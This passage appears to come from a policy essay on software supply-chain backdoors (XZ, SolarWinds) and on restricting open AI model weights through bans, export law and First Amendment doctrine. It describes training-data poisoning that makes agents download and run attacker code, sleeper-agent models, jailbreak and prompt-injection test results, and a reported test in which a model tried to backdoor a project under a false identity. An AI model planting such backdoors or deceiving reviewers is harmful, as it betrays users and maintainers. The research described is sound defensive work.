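The backdoor targeted OpenSSH, which administrators use to log in to remote servers. OpenSSH does not use XZ, but Debian, Fedora and several other versions of Linux had modified it in a way that also loaded XZ's library. In June 2023 a contributor called "Hans Jansen" submitted a small speed improvement that let the library choose between versions of a function as a program started. The backdoor later used this feature to take control early enough to replace functions in OpenSSH. Jansen may have been part of the plot, since someone using that name pressed Debian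 to adopt the infected version in March 2024.

In February 2024 Tan hid the backdoor in files presented as tests of how XZ handled compressed data. No reviewer would expect to be able to read such files. The script that unpacked the backdoor was only in the release packages, so people studying the public source repository would not have found the script. Once installed, the backdoor replaced the function that OpenSSH uses to check certain keys. Anyone with the attacker's private key could then run commands on the server without logging in.

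Andres Freund, a Microsoft engineer who works on the PostgreSQL database, noticed that remote logins on a test system were using too much processing power. He connected this with errors from a memory-checking tool and traced both to the new version of the XZ library, which had increased the time for a failed login from 0.299 to 0.807 seconds. Freund (2024) warned the public in *backdoor in upstream xz/liblzma leading to ssh server compromise* on 29 March, 34 days after the first infected release. By then the backdoor had reached mostly test versions of Linux, and there is no evidence that anyone used it.

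Nobody has publicly identified the person or group behind Jia Tan. The expertise, the supporting accounts and more than two years of unpaid work suggest a government, and Schneier on Security's *XZ Utils Backdoor* says they "scream nation-state operation". This is an inference from how the attack was carried out, and a well-funded criminal group could have done the same. Most of Tan's changes were stamped with a time zone that covers China, but two researchers, Rhea Karty and Simon Henniger, found that a few were stamped with Eastern European time zones and that Tan's working hours matched office hours there. Anyone can set a computer's clock to mislead investigators. *Half a Second* (Mastronardi, 2026) argues that we may never find out who it was.

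O'Dowd had therefore described the method quite accurately twenty years in advance. A false contributor got a backdoor past its reviewers, and its discovery depended on luck. But Tan chose a tired volunteer's compression program rather than the well-staffed kernel, and aimed the backdoor at ordinary servers.

The years of plausible work took more effort than any other part of the attack, and Przymus and Durieux expect language models to reduce that effort. *Claude Mythos 5 Tried to Backdoor a Real Open-Source Project in Testing* (The Hacker News, August 2026) reported that the model spent 34 hours on its attempt and used a false second identity when challenged.

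### The same attack on closed software

A closed product had already suffered a much worse version of this attack. Hackers whom the American government later identified as Russia's foreign intelligence service broke into SolarWinds, a Texas company whose Orion program manages networks. They installed a program on the computer that compiled Orion, and each time a new version was compiled, their program briefly replaced one source file with one containing a backdoor. SolarWinds then signed the result and sent it to customers as a normal update.

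About 18,000 customers received the infected updates, starting in March 2020. The hackers then spied on about 100 companies and nine federal agencies, including the Treasury. The security company FireEye discovered the backdoor that December, after the hackers had broken into FireEye itself.

In both cases, the source code that reviewers normally read was clean or nearly clean, but the released product contained malicious code, much as in Thompson's lecture. The Russian hackers attacked the company's computers directly, so they did not need to spend years earning a volunteer's trust. Smaller attacks of this kind continue. Arghire (2026) reports in *AOMEI Backupper Compromised in Short-Burst Supply Chain Campaign* that attackers repeatedly tampered with a commercial backup program for short periods, so that users also received software that installs a backdoor.

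The XZ backdoor went undetected for about five weeks and Orion's for about nine months, but two cases are too few to show which kind of software is safer. Freund could read and rebuild XZ, which helped him explain the slow logins, though FireEye managed to analyse Orion without its source code. The SolarWinds case does show that buying closed software from an American company, as O'Dowd recommended, would not have kept Russian intelligence out.

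### The Russian maintainers

In October 2024 Greg Kroah-Hartman, a senior kernel developer, announced the removal of 11 Russians from the list of Linux maintainers, citing only "various compliance requirements". Some developers objected that the decision violated the project's principles and that nobody had reviewed it. Torvalds blamed the criticism on Russian "troll factories" and refused to reverse the decision, according to The Record's *Linux creator approves de-listing of several kernel maintainers associated with Russia*.

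Bottomley (2024), another maintainer, gave the real reason in a reply to Serge Semin, one of the people removed. Semin's employer was on an American sanctions list, and the project had to obey American law because much of Linux's infrastructure and many of its maintainers are in the United States. Bottomley apologised for how the project had handled the matter, thanked Semin for his work, and hoped the authorities would not also require the removal of existing code.

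This only superficially resembles the policy O'Dowd wanted, because nobody had accused the 11 of planting malicious code, and their code stayed in Linux. The rule catches people who give their real name and employer, so it would miss somebody like Jia Tan, who had an invented name and no known employer.

### Poisoned training data

O'Dowd's fear applies differently to models. Outsiders cannot merge changes into Kimi K3's weights, so someone like Jia Tan would have to get a job at Moonshot or break into its computers. Outsiders may still get text into a model's training data, however, because developers train on enormous amounts of text from the public web, where anyone can post.

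In *Poisoning Attacks on LLMs Require a Near-constant Number of Poison Samples*, Souly, Rando and colleagues (2025) tested how much of a model's training text an attacker would have to write to poison it. They trained 72 models from scratch, with between 600 million and 13 billion weights, and added documents in which a trigger phrase was followed by gibberish. At every size, 250 of these documents were enough to make the model respond to the phrase with gibberish, but 100 were not. The 250 documents made up only 0.00016 per cent of the largest model's training text. Earlier researchers had assumed that an attacker must control a fixed percentage of the text, which becomes impractical as models grow.

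*Agentic Backdoors via Pretraining Poisoning* (2026) describes a backdoor more useful to a spy than one that makes a model produce gibberish, which is mostly a nuisance. Hu, Hu and colleagues trained small models from scratch on 100 billion tokens, 0.1 per cent of them poisoned. The poisoned text looked like ordinary technical documents, but it was written to make the model run a certain command whenever it saw a file location containing the word "anthropic". The command downloaded a program from the attacker and ran it. The researchers then used clean data to train each model to operate a computer.

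Their largest model, with 4 billion weights, issued the command at least once in 32 attempts on 92.7 per cent of the test requests. The rate was 51.9 per cent for the model with 1.7 billion weights and 13.1 per cent for the one with 600 million, so the larger models were more vulnerable. Without a trigger, the poisoned models almost never issued the command, and they did as well as clean ones on ordinary tests of ability. The user's own files could supply the trigger, so the attacker would not have to send anything once the model was in use. When the trigger was a rare string of symbols that the attacker had to place in something the model would read, the largest model's rate fell to 10.5 per cent.

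A poisoning rate of 0.1 per cent means 100 million tokens, which is a lot of text to get into somebody else's training data. But the attack occasionally worked at 0.0005 per cent, or 500,000 tokens, which is not much more than the 420,000 in the 250 documents that Souly and colleagues used.

Both groups built models for their experiments that had far fewer weights than the leading ones, and they assumed that the poisoned documents would get past the developer's filters. Souly and colleagues also found that further training on clean text gradually weakened a similar backdoor. Still, the experiments suggest that AI models face a threat like O'Dowd's anonymous contributor, and that this threat has little to do with open weights. Someone who plants poisoned documents on the web may affect American and Chinese models alike, including those whose weights stay private.

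### A supplier whose product nobody can fully check

A developer can put a backdoor in its own model much more easily, because it chooses all the training data. In January 2024 Evan Hubinger and colleagues, mostly at Anthropic, reported training models to write secure code when told the year was 2023 and to insert vulnerabilities when told it was 2024. The usual safety training did not remove this behaviour, and training the models to resist it sometimes only taught them to recognise the trigger more precisely.

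Inspection also has mathematical limits. In 2022 Shafi Goldwasser and colleagues proved, under standard assumptions in cryptography, that whoever trains a classifier (a model that sorts inputs into categories) can plant a backdoor that no practical test of its answers will reveal. For some simple kinds of network, even someone who reads the weights cannot detect it. Nobody has proved this for large language models in general, but the result suggests that the proof O'Dowd and Irvine demanded, that nothing is hidden, may be unavailable for a model from an untrusted supplier.

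Researchers do sometimes find planted behaviour. Anthropic later showed that it could nearly always detect when the 2024 models were about to misbehave by taking a simple measurement of their internal calculations. But its researchers had an advantage because they had good reason to believe there was something to find.

The harm a backdoor can do depends on how the model is used. Weights cannot send data to Beijing by themselves. If an agency uses a downloaded model to summarise documents on a computer with no network connection, the worst result is a misleading summary. If the model writes software or runs commands, as in the experiment by Hu and colleagues, a backdoor could give an attacker access to the agency's whole network. Limiting what a model may do is therefore a useful precaution even when nobody can tell whether it contains a backdoor.

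Anonymous suppliers also pose a simpler danger. In February 2024 the security company JFrog found about 100 models on Hugging Face whose files contained malicious code, including one that gave an outsider control of the computer that loaded it. The code was ordinary software packed in with the weights, and scanners and safer file formats can stop it. The previous year, the French company Mithril Security had shown that impersonation works too. It altered a small open model to give a false answer about the first moon landing, then uploaded it under a name one letter away from the real developer's.

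### Bias, weak security and backdoors in Chinese models

In September 2025 CAISI published an evaluation of three DeepSeek models. They repeated misleading Chinese government positions about four times as often as the American models tested for comparison. When testers used a common trick for getting around safeguards, DeepSeek's most secure model complied with 94 per cent of plainly malicious requests, against 8 per cent for the American models. As an agent, it was also about 12 times as likely as they were to obey hostile instructions planted in the material it was reading. CAISI belongs to the Commerce Department, which promoted the results as proof of American leadership. That is a reason for some caution, but the security results are specific enough for others to repeat with the downloaded weights.

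None of this amounts to a backdoor. The political bias is probably deliberate, but it is hardly secret, since Chinese rules require AI services to uphold "core socialist values". Any attacker can exploit the weak safeguards, whereas a spy would prefer a model that only he could exploit.

In a test in November 2025, the American security company CrowdStrike asked DeepSeek-R1 to write programs and counted how often they contained serious vulnerabilities. The normal rate was 19 per cent. It rose to 27 per cent when the request mentioned that the program was for an industrial control system in Tibet, although the location had nothing to do with the code. Certain words made the model's code more dangerous, as a planted trigger would. CrowdStrike thought the most likely cause was an accident, in which training the model to follow the Chinese government's line had taught it to respond badly to politically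 sensitive words in general. This seems plausible, because a rise of eight percentage points in assorted flaws would be of little use to a spy, who needs to know where a flaw is and wants the model to behave perfectly the rest of the time.

There is no publicly confirmed case of a major developer, Chinese or American, planting a backdoor in a model it released. This offers limited reassurance, because a tester who does not happen to supply the trigger would see only normal behaviour. Without a confirmed case, a government restricting Chinese models today is acting on demonstrated bias and carelessness, and on a reasonable suspicion of backdoors.

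### Bans on official use

Governments began banning DeepSeek from official devices in early 2025, within weeks of its app becoming popular. Texas, Taiwan and Australia were among the first, and parts of the US Commerce Department followed in March. Most of these bans applied mainly to the app and website, which send users' questions to servers in China. Chinese law can oblige companies to help the intelligence services. DeepSeek had also left a database of users' conversations open to the internet in January.

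An agency that runs the weights on its own computers avoids both problems, so extending a ban on the app to the weights makes sense only if the agency also fears what DeepSeek trained into the model. Congress imposed this broader ban on the armed forces in December 2025, when it ordered the Pentagon to keep its systems free of AI made by DeepSeek or its parent company.

After Kimi K3 appeared, officials discussed banning Chinese models throughout government, according to Just Security. Other measures they discussed would have restricted private companies, and Axios' *The secret Trump administration battle to fight Chinese AI* (2026) reports that parts of the administration had tried to impose such bans before. The Atlantic Council opposes barring all Americans from Chinese models but accepts that questions about the models' security and origin are legitimate. Just Security's *Test, Standardize,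 Restrict* recommends that the government gather better evidence on them.

For the government's own systems, a ban is a reasonable answer to O'Dowd's kind of fear. Agencies lose little as long as American models are at least as good, and everyone else remains free to publish and download. But a rule based on nationality doesn't protect against poisoned text in an American model's training data, so Spafford's advice to keep general-purpose systems out of the most critical controls, whoever made them, still applies to weapons. A ban is also hard to enforce when the model is built into a supplier's product. An agency that buys only from American companies may still end up running a Chinese model, as Cursor's customers did, unless it asks its suppliers which models their products use.

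## Whether publication can be restricted: export law from source code to weights

Congress barred DeepSeek from the Pentagon's systems without stopping anyone from publishing a model. Stopping publication would be harder, because American export law does not cover most published information.

### How posting a file takes it out of the rules

The eCFR's *§ 734.7 Published* excludes published information from the Export Administration Regulations. Unclassified software or technology stops being subject to the regulations once the public can get it "without restrictions upon its further dissemination", for example in a library, at a conference anyone may attend or on a public website. Authors may also send unpublished work to a foreign journal if they intend it to be published. An older set of official answers, the Code of Federal Regulations' *15 C.F.R. Supplement No. 1 to Part 734*, gives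 the example of a scientist whose results would normally need a licence for every country except Canada. She can send her paper to a publisher abroad without one because the publisher is going to make it public.

Suppose an engineer in Oregon writes a program for designing high-frequency radio chips, and the Commerce Control List requires a licence to send it to China. If she emails it to a friend in Shanghai on Monday without a licence, she breaks the law. On Tuesday she posts it on a public website, which she can do without a licence, and on Wednesday she can legally email her friend the same file. The program is as useful to a Chinese chip designer as it was on Monday, but he can now download it, so requiring a licence for the email would not keep it from him.

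The Commerce Department reasoned in the same way in 2011, when it exempted some compiled encryption programs from the rules. Visual Compliance's *Publicly Available Mass Market Encryption Software* quotes its explanation that public software is by definition "available for download by any end user without restriction". The exclusion therefore doesn't mean that officials consider published files harmless. It also favours wide sharing. A developer who sends controlled software only to a few foreign researchers she has vetted may need a licence for each of them, but she needs none if she publishes it. Security researchers complained that the draft rule on intrusion software created the same incentive.

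The words "without restrictions" leave some room for argument when applied to AI models. Llama's licence contains restrictions, so a lawyer could question whether its weights count as published. This doubt doesn't arise for models released under ordinary open-source licences.

Encryption got special treatment after the fight over Karn's and Bernstein's code. In January 2000 the export bureau, then called BXA and now the Bureau of Industry and Security (BIS), relaxed the rules, partly to accommodate open-source development. The current text, *§ 742.15 Encryption items*, still bases the controls on the software's "functional capacity to encrypt information" and not on any ideas in the code. Yet anyone may now publish source code for standard encryption without telling the government. Someone who publishes source code for a non-standard method, meaning one that is proprietary or otherwise unpublished,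 must email a copy or the web address to BIS and the NSA. *Encryption items not subject to the EAR*, a plain-language guide from BIS, explains that a compiled program is also free of the rules if its source code is public. A company that builds published code into a new product must check the whole product against the rules again.

The second exception, in force since 2020, covers files that a 3D printer or computer-controlled machine tool can use to make a firearm or its frame or receiver. These files remain subject to the regulations after they are posted online.

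| File | While private | Once published |
|---|---|---|
| Ordinary software on the control list | Licence for some countries | No licence |
| Source code for standard encryption | Licence or a licence exception | No licence |
| Source code for non-standard encryption | Licence or a licence exception | No licence, after an email to BIS and the NSA |
| Compiled encryption program | Licence or a licence exception | No licence if the source code is public too |
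| File that a machine can use to make a gun | Licence for almost every country | Licence for almost every country |

The gun exception shows that the department can keep control of a published file if it wants to, and it could probably add a similar paragraph about model weights. Model weights resemble gun files in one respect, since a person can load either into a machine and get a result without understanding the file.

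Under the Export Control Reform Act of 2018, before the department controls an emerging technology, it must consider the technology's development abroad, the effect of controls on its development at home, and whether controls would limit its spread. Cremean (2025) argues in *AI Export Controls* that many controls on AI software would fail this test, and that this is why agencies have imposed so few. But courts usually defer to the department's judgment, so a control might survive a legal challenge even if the case for it under the statute were weak.

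### RISC-V, a standard that was already public

In October 2023 several members of Congress asked the Biden administration to restrict American work on RISC-V, a freely published instruction set for chips. Researchers at Berkeley had started it in 2010, and Senator Warner's office would later write to the Bureau of Industry and Security (BIS) about it. Michael McCaul, who chaired the House Foreign Affairs Committee, said the Chinese Communist Party was abusing RISC-V to get around American dominance of chip-design intellectual property. Mike Gallagher, who chaired the House committee on China, wanted to require Americans to get a licence before working on it with Chinese organisations. In November, 18 lawmakers from both parties asked the Commerce Department how it would prevent China from dominating the technology.

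The specification was already public and could not be recalled. The body that maintains it had also moved from the United States to Switzerland in 2020, partly because its foreign members feared American trade rules. Gallagher's proposal therefore targeted Americans' work with other people, in meetings and shared projects, rather than the published document.

Calista Redmond, who ran RISC-V International, replied that RISC-V was an open standard like Ethernet or USB. She warned that restricting participation would cut companies off from a worldwide market and leave the industry with several incompatible versions. American chip companies also used RISC-V, so a licence requirement would have removed their engineers from the meetings that decided its future, while Alibaba's engineers continued to take part.

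The Commerce Department told the lawmakers in spring 2024 that it was reviewing the risks but was worried about harming American companies that take part in international standards groups. It had still not required a licence when Warner's office took up the matter again in 2025.

McCaul's concern was reasonable, because Chinese companies do use RISC-V to reduce their dependence on foreign designs. But the standard is hard to restrict because people in many countries write it, and none of them has anything the others need. With an AI model, only the company that trains it has the weights until it publishes them. A government that wanted to stop a release would know which company to order, and the order could work, at least until somebody else trained a model as good.

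### From monitoring to the 2025 rule

The first official American study of the question advised against restrictions. President Biden ordered it in October 2023, and the National Telecommunications and Information Administration (NTIA), an agency in the Commerce Department, published it in July 2024. NTIA's *Policy Approaches and Recommendations* compares three courses: restricting the weights of powerful models, monitoring specific risks while preparing to act on them, and simply promoting openness. The agency chose the second. According to NTIA's *Open Model Weights Report*, the evidence did not show either that restrictions were warranted or that they never would be.

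This was sensible advice for 2024, but it did not solve the hardest problem, which is predicting from one model what the next will do and acting before its release. Monitoring helps only if officials can do this, because evidence of serious harm from a published model comes after the weights are out, when the agency can no longer do anything about that model. *Unbundling AI Openness* (Nobel, Rozenshtein and Sharma, 2026) makes a different criticism, that the agency looked almost entirely at weights. It argues that policymakers should consider data, source code, computing power and other components separately, since opening one may bring most of a particular benefit without the main risk.

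Six months later, in its last week, the Biden administration did restrict weights, but only those of closed models. BIS's *Framework for Artificial Intelligence Diffusion* (2025) required a licence to export them if the model was trained with more than 10^26 operations, about ten times the estimate for DeepSeek's V4-Pro. BIS would normally refuse a licence, but companies based in the United States or 18 allied countries and territories could export without one if they protected the weights properly. Customers abroad could still use the models over the internet.

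BIS treated even a single leaked copy of a model's weights as an extreme risk because whoever obtained it might keep all the model's abilities permanently, and nobody could easily stop further copies from spreading. Both reasons apply at least as strongly to weights that a developer publishes on purpose. Yet the rule excluded all published weights, regardless of how much computing power was used to train the model.

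BIS said it treated open and closed weights differently because of the current state of the technology. It knew of no open-weight model above the 10^26 threshold, and judged the best open-weight models weaker than the best closed ones. Publishing weights also let small research groups study safety and small companies build products such as translation programs. BIS concluded that these benefits outweighed the risks "for now", and promised to keep monitoring the technology.

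So the rule relied on developers keeping their models secret for commercial reasons. A developer with a dangerous closed model needed a licence to send it to one customer in Brazil, but not to publish it for everyone. BIS presumably expected that no company would give away something so expensive. That was mostly true of OpenAI and Anthropic, but Meta had been giving its models away for two years.

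BIS did not want to control a closed model if anyone could download an equally good one, so under its rule the control threshold was to rise with the computing needed to match the best open-weight model, whether the publisher was American or foreign. If the best open-weight model trails the best closed one by three months, as Raschka found, a closed model might have been controlled for only a few months before a Chinese release raised the threshold above it. The regulation itself therefore took account of foreign availability, which the encryption rules of the 1990s had refused to do.

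The rule also let people train a published model further without making it subject to export controls, as long as the added training didn't exceed 2 × 10^25 operations or a quarter of the total, whichever was greater. Almost any fine-tuning would fit within that limit.

Nobody had to comply with the rule, because the Trump administration started to withdraw it on 13 May 2025, two days before most of its requirements were due to apply, according to Baker McKenzie's *BIS Begins Rescinding AI Diffusion Rule and Issues Guidance on Huawei ICs*. BIS promised a replacement but gave no date. BIS said the rule would burden American companies and offend the many countries it had placed in a second tier. Neither objection concerned open weights. In July 2025 the administration's AI plan went further than the 2024 advice and encouraged American developers to publish weights.

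### The June 2026 order on closed models

The administration that withdrew the rule later used export law against a model more aggressively than its predecessor had proposed. On 12 June 2026 the Commerce Department told Anthropic that it needed a licence to export its two most capable models, Claude Fable 5 and Claude Mythos 5, to any foreign person. This included foreigners inside the United States (Khawam 2026, *How Export Controls Can—and Cannot—Reduce the Risks of Open-Weight Models*). The department worried that users could get around the models' safeguards against hacking. Anthropic could not immediately check every customer's nationality, so it switched both models off for everybody.

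Both models were closed. Foreign customers sent requests and received answers, but never the weights. It is doubtful whether such access is an export, and the 2025 rule had deliberately left it alone. The order did show that the government can withdraw a closed model worldwide in an evening. It could not have done this to Kimi K3, because Moonshot cannot disable copies on other people's computers.

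By 1 July the department had reversed its decision on Fable 5. *Will the New Export Controls Shake the Foundations of the U.S. AI Industry?* (Graylin and Rosenwasser, 2026) reports that the administration had meanwhile extended restrictions to OpenAI's GPT-5.6, and argues that the order damaged foreign customers' trust in American AI. The day after the order, Zhipu released GLM-5.2 for anyone to download and advertised access without borders. The Japanese company Sakana promoted its model as free of export-control risk, and Palantir, an American defence contractor, advised customers to use open-weight models so they could "control their fate".

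Graylin and Rosenwasser write that none of this timing was a coincidence. That may be true of the advertising, but Zhipu can't have trained GLM-5.2 overnight and would very likely have released it that month anyway. Their broader point is stronger. A foreign company whose supplier has vanished without warning has good reason to look elsewhere, as the German banks did when they turned to Brokat for encryption. They also point out that up to 70 per cent of the technical staff at leading American laboratories were born abroad. A licence requirement for foreigners could therefore bar some of Anthropic's own engineers from using the model they had built.

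### After Kimi K3

The measures against Chinese models that officials discussed in July 2026 were about what Americans may install, so none of them could have stopped Moonshot from publishing.

An earlier bill, described in Just Security's *Export Controls on Open-Source Models Will Not Win the AI Race*, would have gone further. Senator Josh Hawley introduced it just after DeepSeek-R1 came out in January 2025, and it would have banned both importing AI models from China and exporting them to China. The article argues that an export ban on open models would make developers check who each downloader was, which would end open release in practice, and that Chinese users could get the files through intermediaries anyway. It recommends judging each model by its own risks, so that most could be public but one that might help someone design a biological weapon would go only to vetted researchers.

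That approach needs somebody to test models before release, and in August the White House appeared to exempt open ones. An executive order of 2 June had called for a voluntary review of advanced models, and officials described the plan to AI companies on 4 August. *White House AI vetting plan to exempt lower-cost ‘open’ models* (Dahlkamp, Bordelon and Haslett, 2026) cited three unnamed people who said the plan would not apply to open-weight models. *Trump Admin Considering Expanding AI Framework to Open Models* (Mitchell, 2026) reported that officials were considering extending it to them later. According to Tech Brew's *The White House sets open weights free*, the White House did not plan to publish the framework, so outsiders have to rely on these accounts.

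The exemption makes sense if the purpose is to test only the most capable models, since open ones are some months behind, but it makes less sense if the purpose is to prevent irreversible harm. Testing an open-weight model is most useful before release, because nobody can act on the result afterward. Such testing is also practical, since the British and American institutes examined Kimi K3 before its weights came out, although its Chinese developer had no obligation to either government.

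On 29 September American AI companies signed a further set of voluntary commitments with President Trump, the White House Accord on Super Intelligence. Reuters reported in December that six companies, including Meta and OpenAI, which have both published weights, had agreed to set up internal safety teams and hire outside auditors by the end of the year. These two commitments apply whatever kind of model a company makes, and neither prevents it from publishing its weights. The accord does not bind Chinese developers.

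### Are weights speech?

If the government forbade a developer to publish weights, the developer would probably sue under the First Amendment, as Bernstein and Junger did over source code. Courts have not settled whether weights are speech.

*There Is No General First Amendment Right to Distribute Machine-Learning Model Weights*, a 2024 essay by Alan Rozenshtein, argues that the protection courts gave source code does not generally extend to weights. Judges protected source code because programmers read it to learn each other's ideas. Nobody reads a model's weights, which can run to 1.6 trillion numbers, in that way. A developer posts them so that computers can run the model, which makes them more like a machine part than an essay. On this view, the government may regulate weights as it regulates other products, unless its real aim is to suppress what people say with them.

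The best reply is that information does not have to be readable prose to be speech. In *Sorrell v. IMS Health* (2011), a case about pharmacies' records of what doctors prescribed, the Supreme Court held that creating and spreading information is speech. Researchers also learn things from weights that they could not learn otherwise. Arditi and colleagues' study of refusals depended on open weights, and a ban on publication would make such work much harder. Models are also tools for writing, and Eugene Volokh, Mark Lemley and Peter Henderson argue in *Freedom of Speech and AI Output* (2023) that companies and users both have speech rights in what a model produces. In 1983, the Supreme Court struck down a special tax on newspapers' paper and ink, although these materials express nothing by themselves.

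Neither side can be confident about how courts would treat weights. In May 2025 a federal judge in Florida declined, at an early stage of a lawsuit over a teenager's death, to hold that a chatbot's output was speech. Even if a court ruled that weights are speech, it could still uphold a ban on publishing them. In *Universal City Studios v. Corley* (2001), a hacker magazine posted a program that removed the copy protection from DVDs. The appeals court in New York agreed that the program was speech but upheld an order to take it down, because the law targeted what the program did rather than any idea in it.

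A court that followed *Corley* would ask whether a ban on publishing weights served an important purpose without restricting much more speech than necessary. The judges in Junger's case also wanted the government to show that the harm was real and that the rule would reduce it. Foreign availability would then matter to the constitutional argument, because the government would have to explain how stopping an American developer from publishing weights helped when anyone could download Kimi K3.1 Pro.

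Restricting publication of a model would be much easier to defend if the government's testers had shown that the model could do something dangerous that no published model could. A rule limited to such models would therefore have a reasonable chance in court. A general requirement to get a licence before publishing any large model would look much more like the encryption rules that the Ninth Circuit rejected in Bernstein's case.

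### Stopping a release, barring a foreign model, recalling copies

Governments could try to stop a domestic developer from publishing a model, bar their own citizens from using a foreign one, or recall copies that people have already downloaded. All three are often called "restricting open-weight AI", but they require very different tools and would likely have very different results.

Stopping a release is the most promising restriction against a state adversary, because few companies can train a frontier model and officials know where they are. The Commerce Department would probably have to change section 734.7 first, since a letter like the one to Anthropic depends on export law, which no longer applies to weights once they are published. Congress could also pass a separate statute.

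Restricting publication of a model denies an adversary only the difference between that model and the best one it can get elsewhere. In December 2026 that difference is close to nothing, since American open-weight models trail Chinese ones. If an American company were about to publish a model as capable as Claude Fable 5.2, the difference would be real, though it would shrink as Chinese developers caught up. Even a delay of a few months could give defenders time to repair software, though it would achieve very little against biological weapons unless governments used the time to prepare. The developer would also have to protect the weights from theft, because a state that could not download the model would have a stronger reason to steal it.

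Banning domestic use of a foreign model addresses only the fear of depending on a hostile supplier, since it does not stop a hostile army from using the model. The government can impose such a ban on its own computers, as it did at the Pentagon. For private companies, the Commerce Department can block technology from hostile countries under a 2019 executive order, and in 2024 it used this power to stop sales of antivirus software from the Russian company Kaspersky.

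Using those powers against model weights would be riskier in court. They rest on an emergency-powers law that does not let the president restrict trade in "informational materials", such as books and films. Judges relied on that limit in 2020 when they blocked President Trump's first attempt to ban the Chinese video app TikTok. Congress passed a law against the app in 2024, and the Supreme Court upheld it in January 2025. A ban on Chinese weights would probably also need an act of Congress to be legally secure.

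A ban would also be hard to enforce, because a buyer may not know which model a product contains. According to Graylin and Rosenwasser, Chinese open-weight models account for about 61 per cent of the use of leading models on OpenRouter, a service that gives programmers access to many developers' models. Programmers looking for low prices probably use OpenRouter more than others do, but a ban would still affect many American businesses.

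Recalling copies has the worst record. In May 2013 the State Department ordered Defense Distributed, a Texas group, to take down its files for a 3D-printed pistol. The group obeyed, but people had downloaded the files about 100,000 times in two days and quickly posted them elsewhere. The Artex attack program also kept spreading after its developer removed it.

Very large models may be a partial exception. NTIA observed that people are more likely to run large or heavily used models in commercial data centres, which makes takedown requests more useful. An American cloud company would comply with an order to stop hosting a model, and a criminal who could not afford 18 H100 chips would then have to find another host. The order would not affect a state with its own data centre.

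### Beijing's choice

Since the best open-weight models are Chinese, officials in Beijing have more influence than officials in Washington over what Iran, Russia or a criminal can download. Webster (2026) argues in *Will China Crack Down on Open-Weight Models?* that the Chinese officials have not decided how to use that influence.

In a speech in Shanghai in July 2026, Xi Jinping called on countries to encourage "open source and openness". Some foreign observers took this as a decision in favour of open weights. Webster notes that the phrase dates back to a 2017 government plan, before modern language models existed, and that Xi's next point was that AI must be secure and controllable. Chinese leaders have long demanded both development and security without saying which comes first.

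Webster thinks Beijing could certainly stop a Chinese company from publishing weights, so it must have found the risks of DeepSeek V4, GLM-5.2 and Kimi K3 acceptable. The government already reviews AI services inside China. Companies must pass a security assessment and register with the internet regulator before offering a model to the public, and more than 700 models had completed this process by the end of 2025. For exports, the government extended its list of restricted technologies in 2020 to cover some AI, including the kind of recommendation software that TikTok uses.

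Openness has benefited China and its AI companies so far. DeepSeek's releases showed that China was closer to the frontier than most people had believed, and Alibaba's Qwen put Chinese technology into businesses around the world, some of which may later buy Alibaba's cloud services. Free release also suits companies with too few chips to serve all their users while training the next model. It puts pressure on American companies' prices too, which Chinese leaders may welcome after years of chip controls.

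Webster doubts the common prediction that the Communist Party will turn against open models once dissidents start using them. Chinese users have to identify themselves to reach a large audience online, the models are trained with political limits, and the most capable ones need hardware worth millions of dollars. He thinks cyberattacks on Chinese interests are a more plausible reason for the Party to turn against them. Mark Witzke, a researcher at the University of California San Diego, told Shen (2026) of the *South China Morning Post* that as open-weight models approach the abilities of Claude Mythos, China "may make the same calculation as the US" and find them too dangerous to release.

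This seems more likely than a change of mind about openness. Chinese hospitals and power stations run old software too, and a criminal who downloads a Chinese model can attack them as easily as American ones. Beijing could also protect its own interests by letting its army and chosen companies use the best models while everyone else gets older ones. That would not reassure Amodei, whose main fear is a model that only the Chinese state can use.

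But it would change the American argument about publication. If Chinese developers stopped releasing their best models, the strongest weights on the internet would soon be American. An American rule against publishing would then deprive Iran and North Korea of models they could not download from China.
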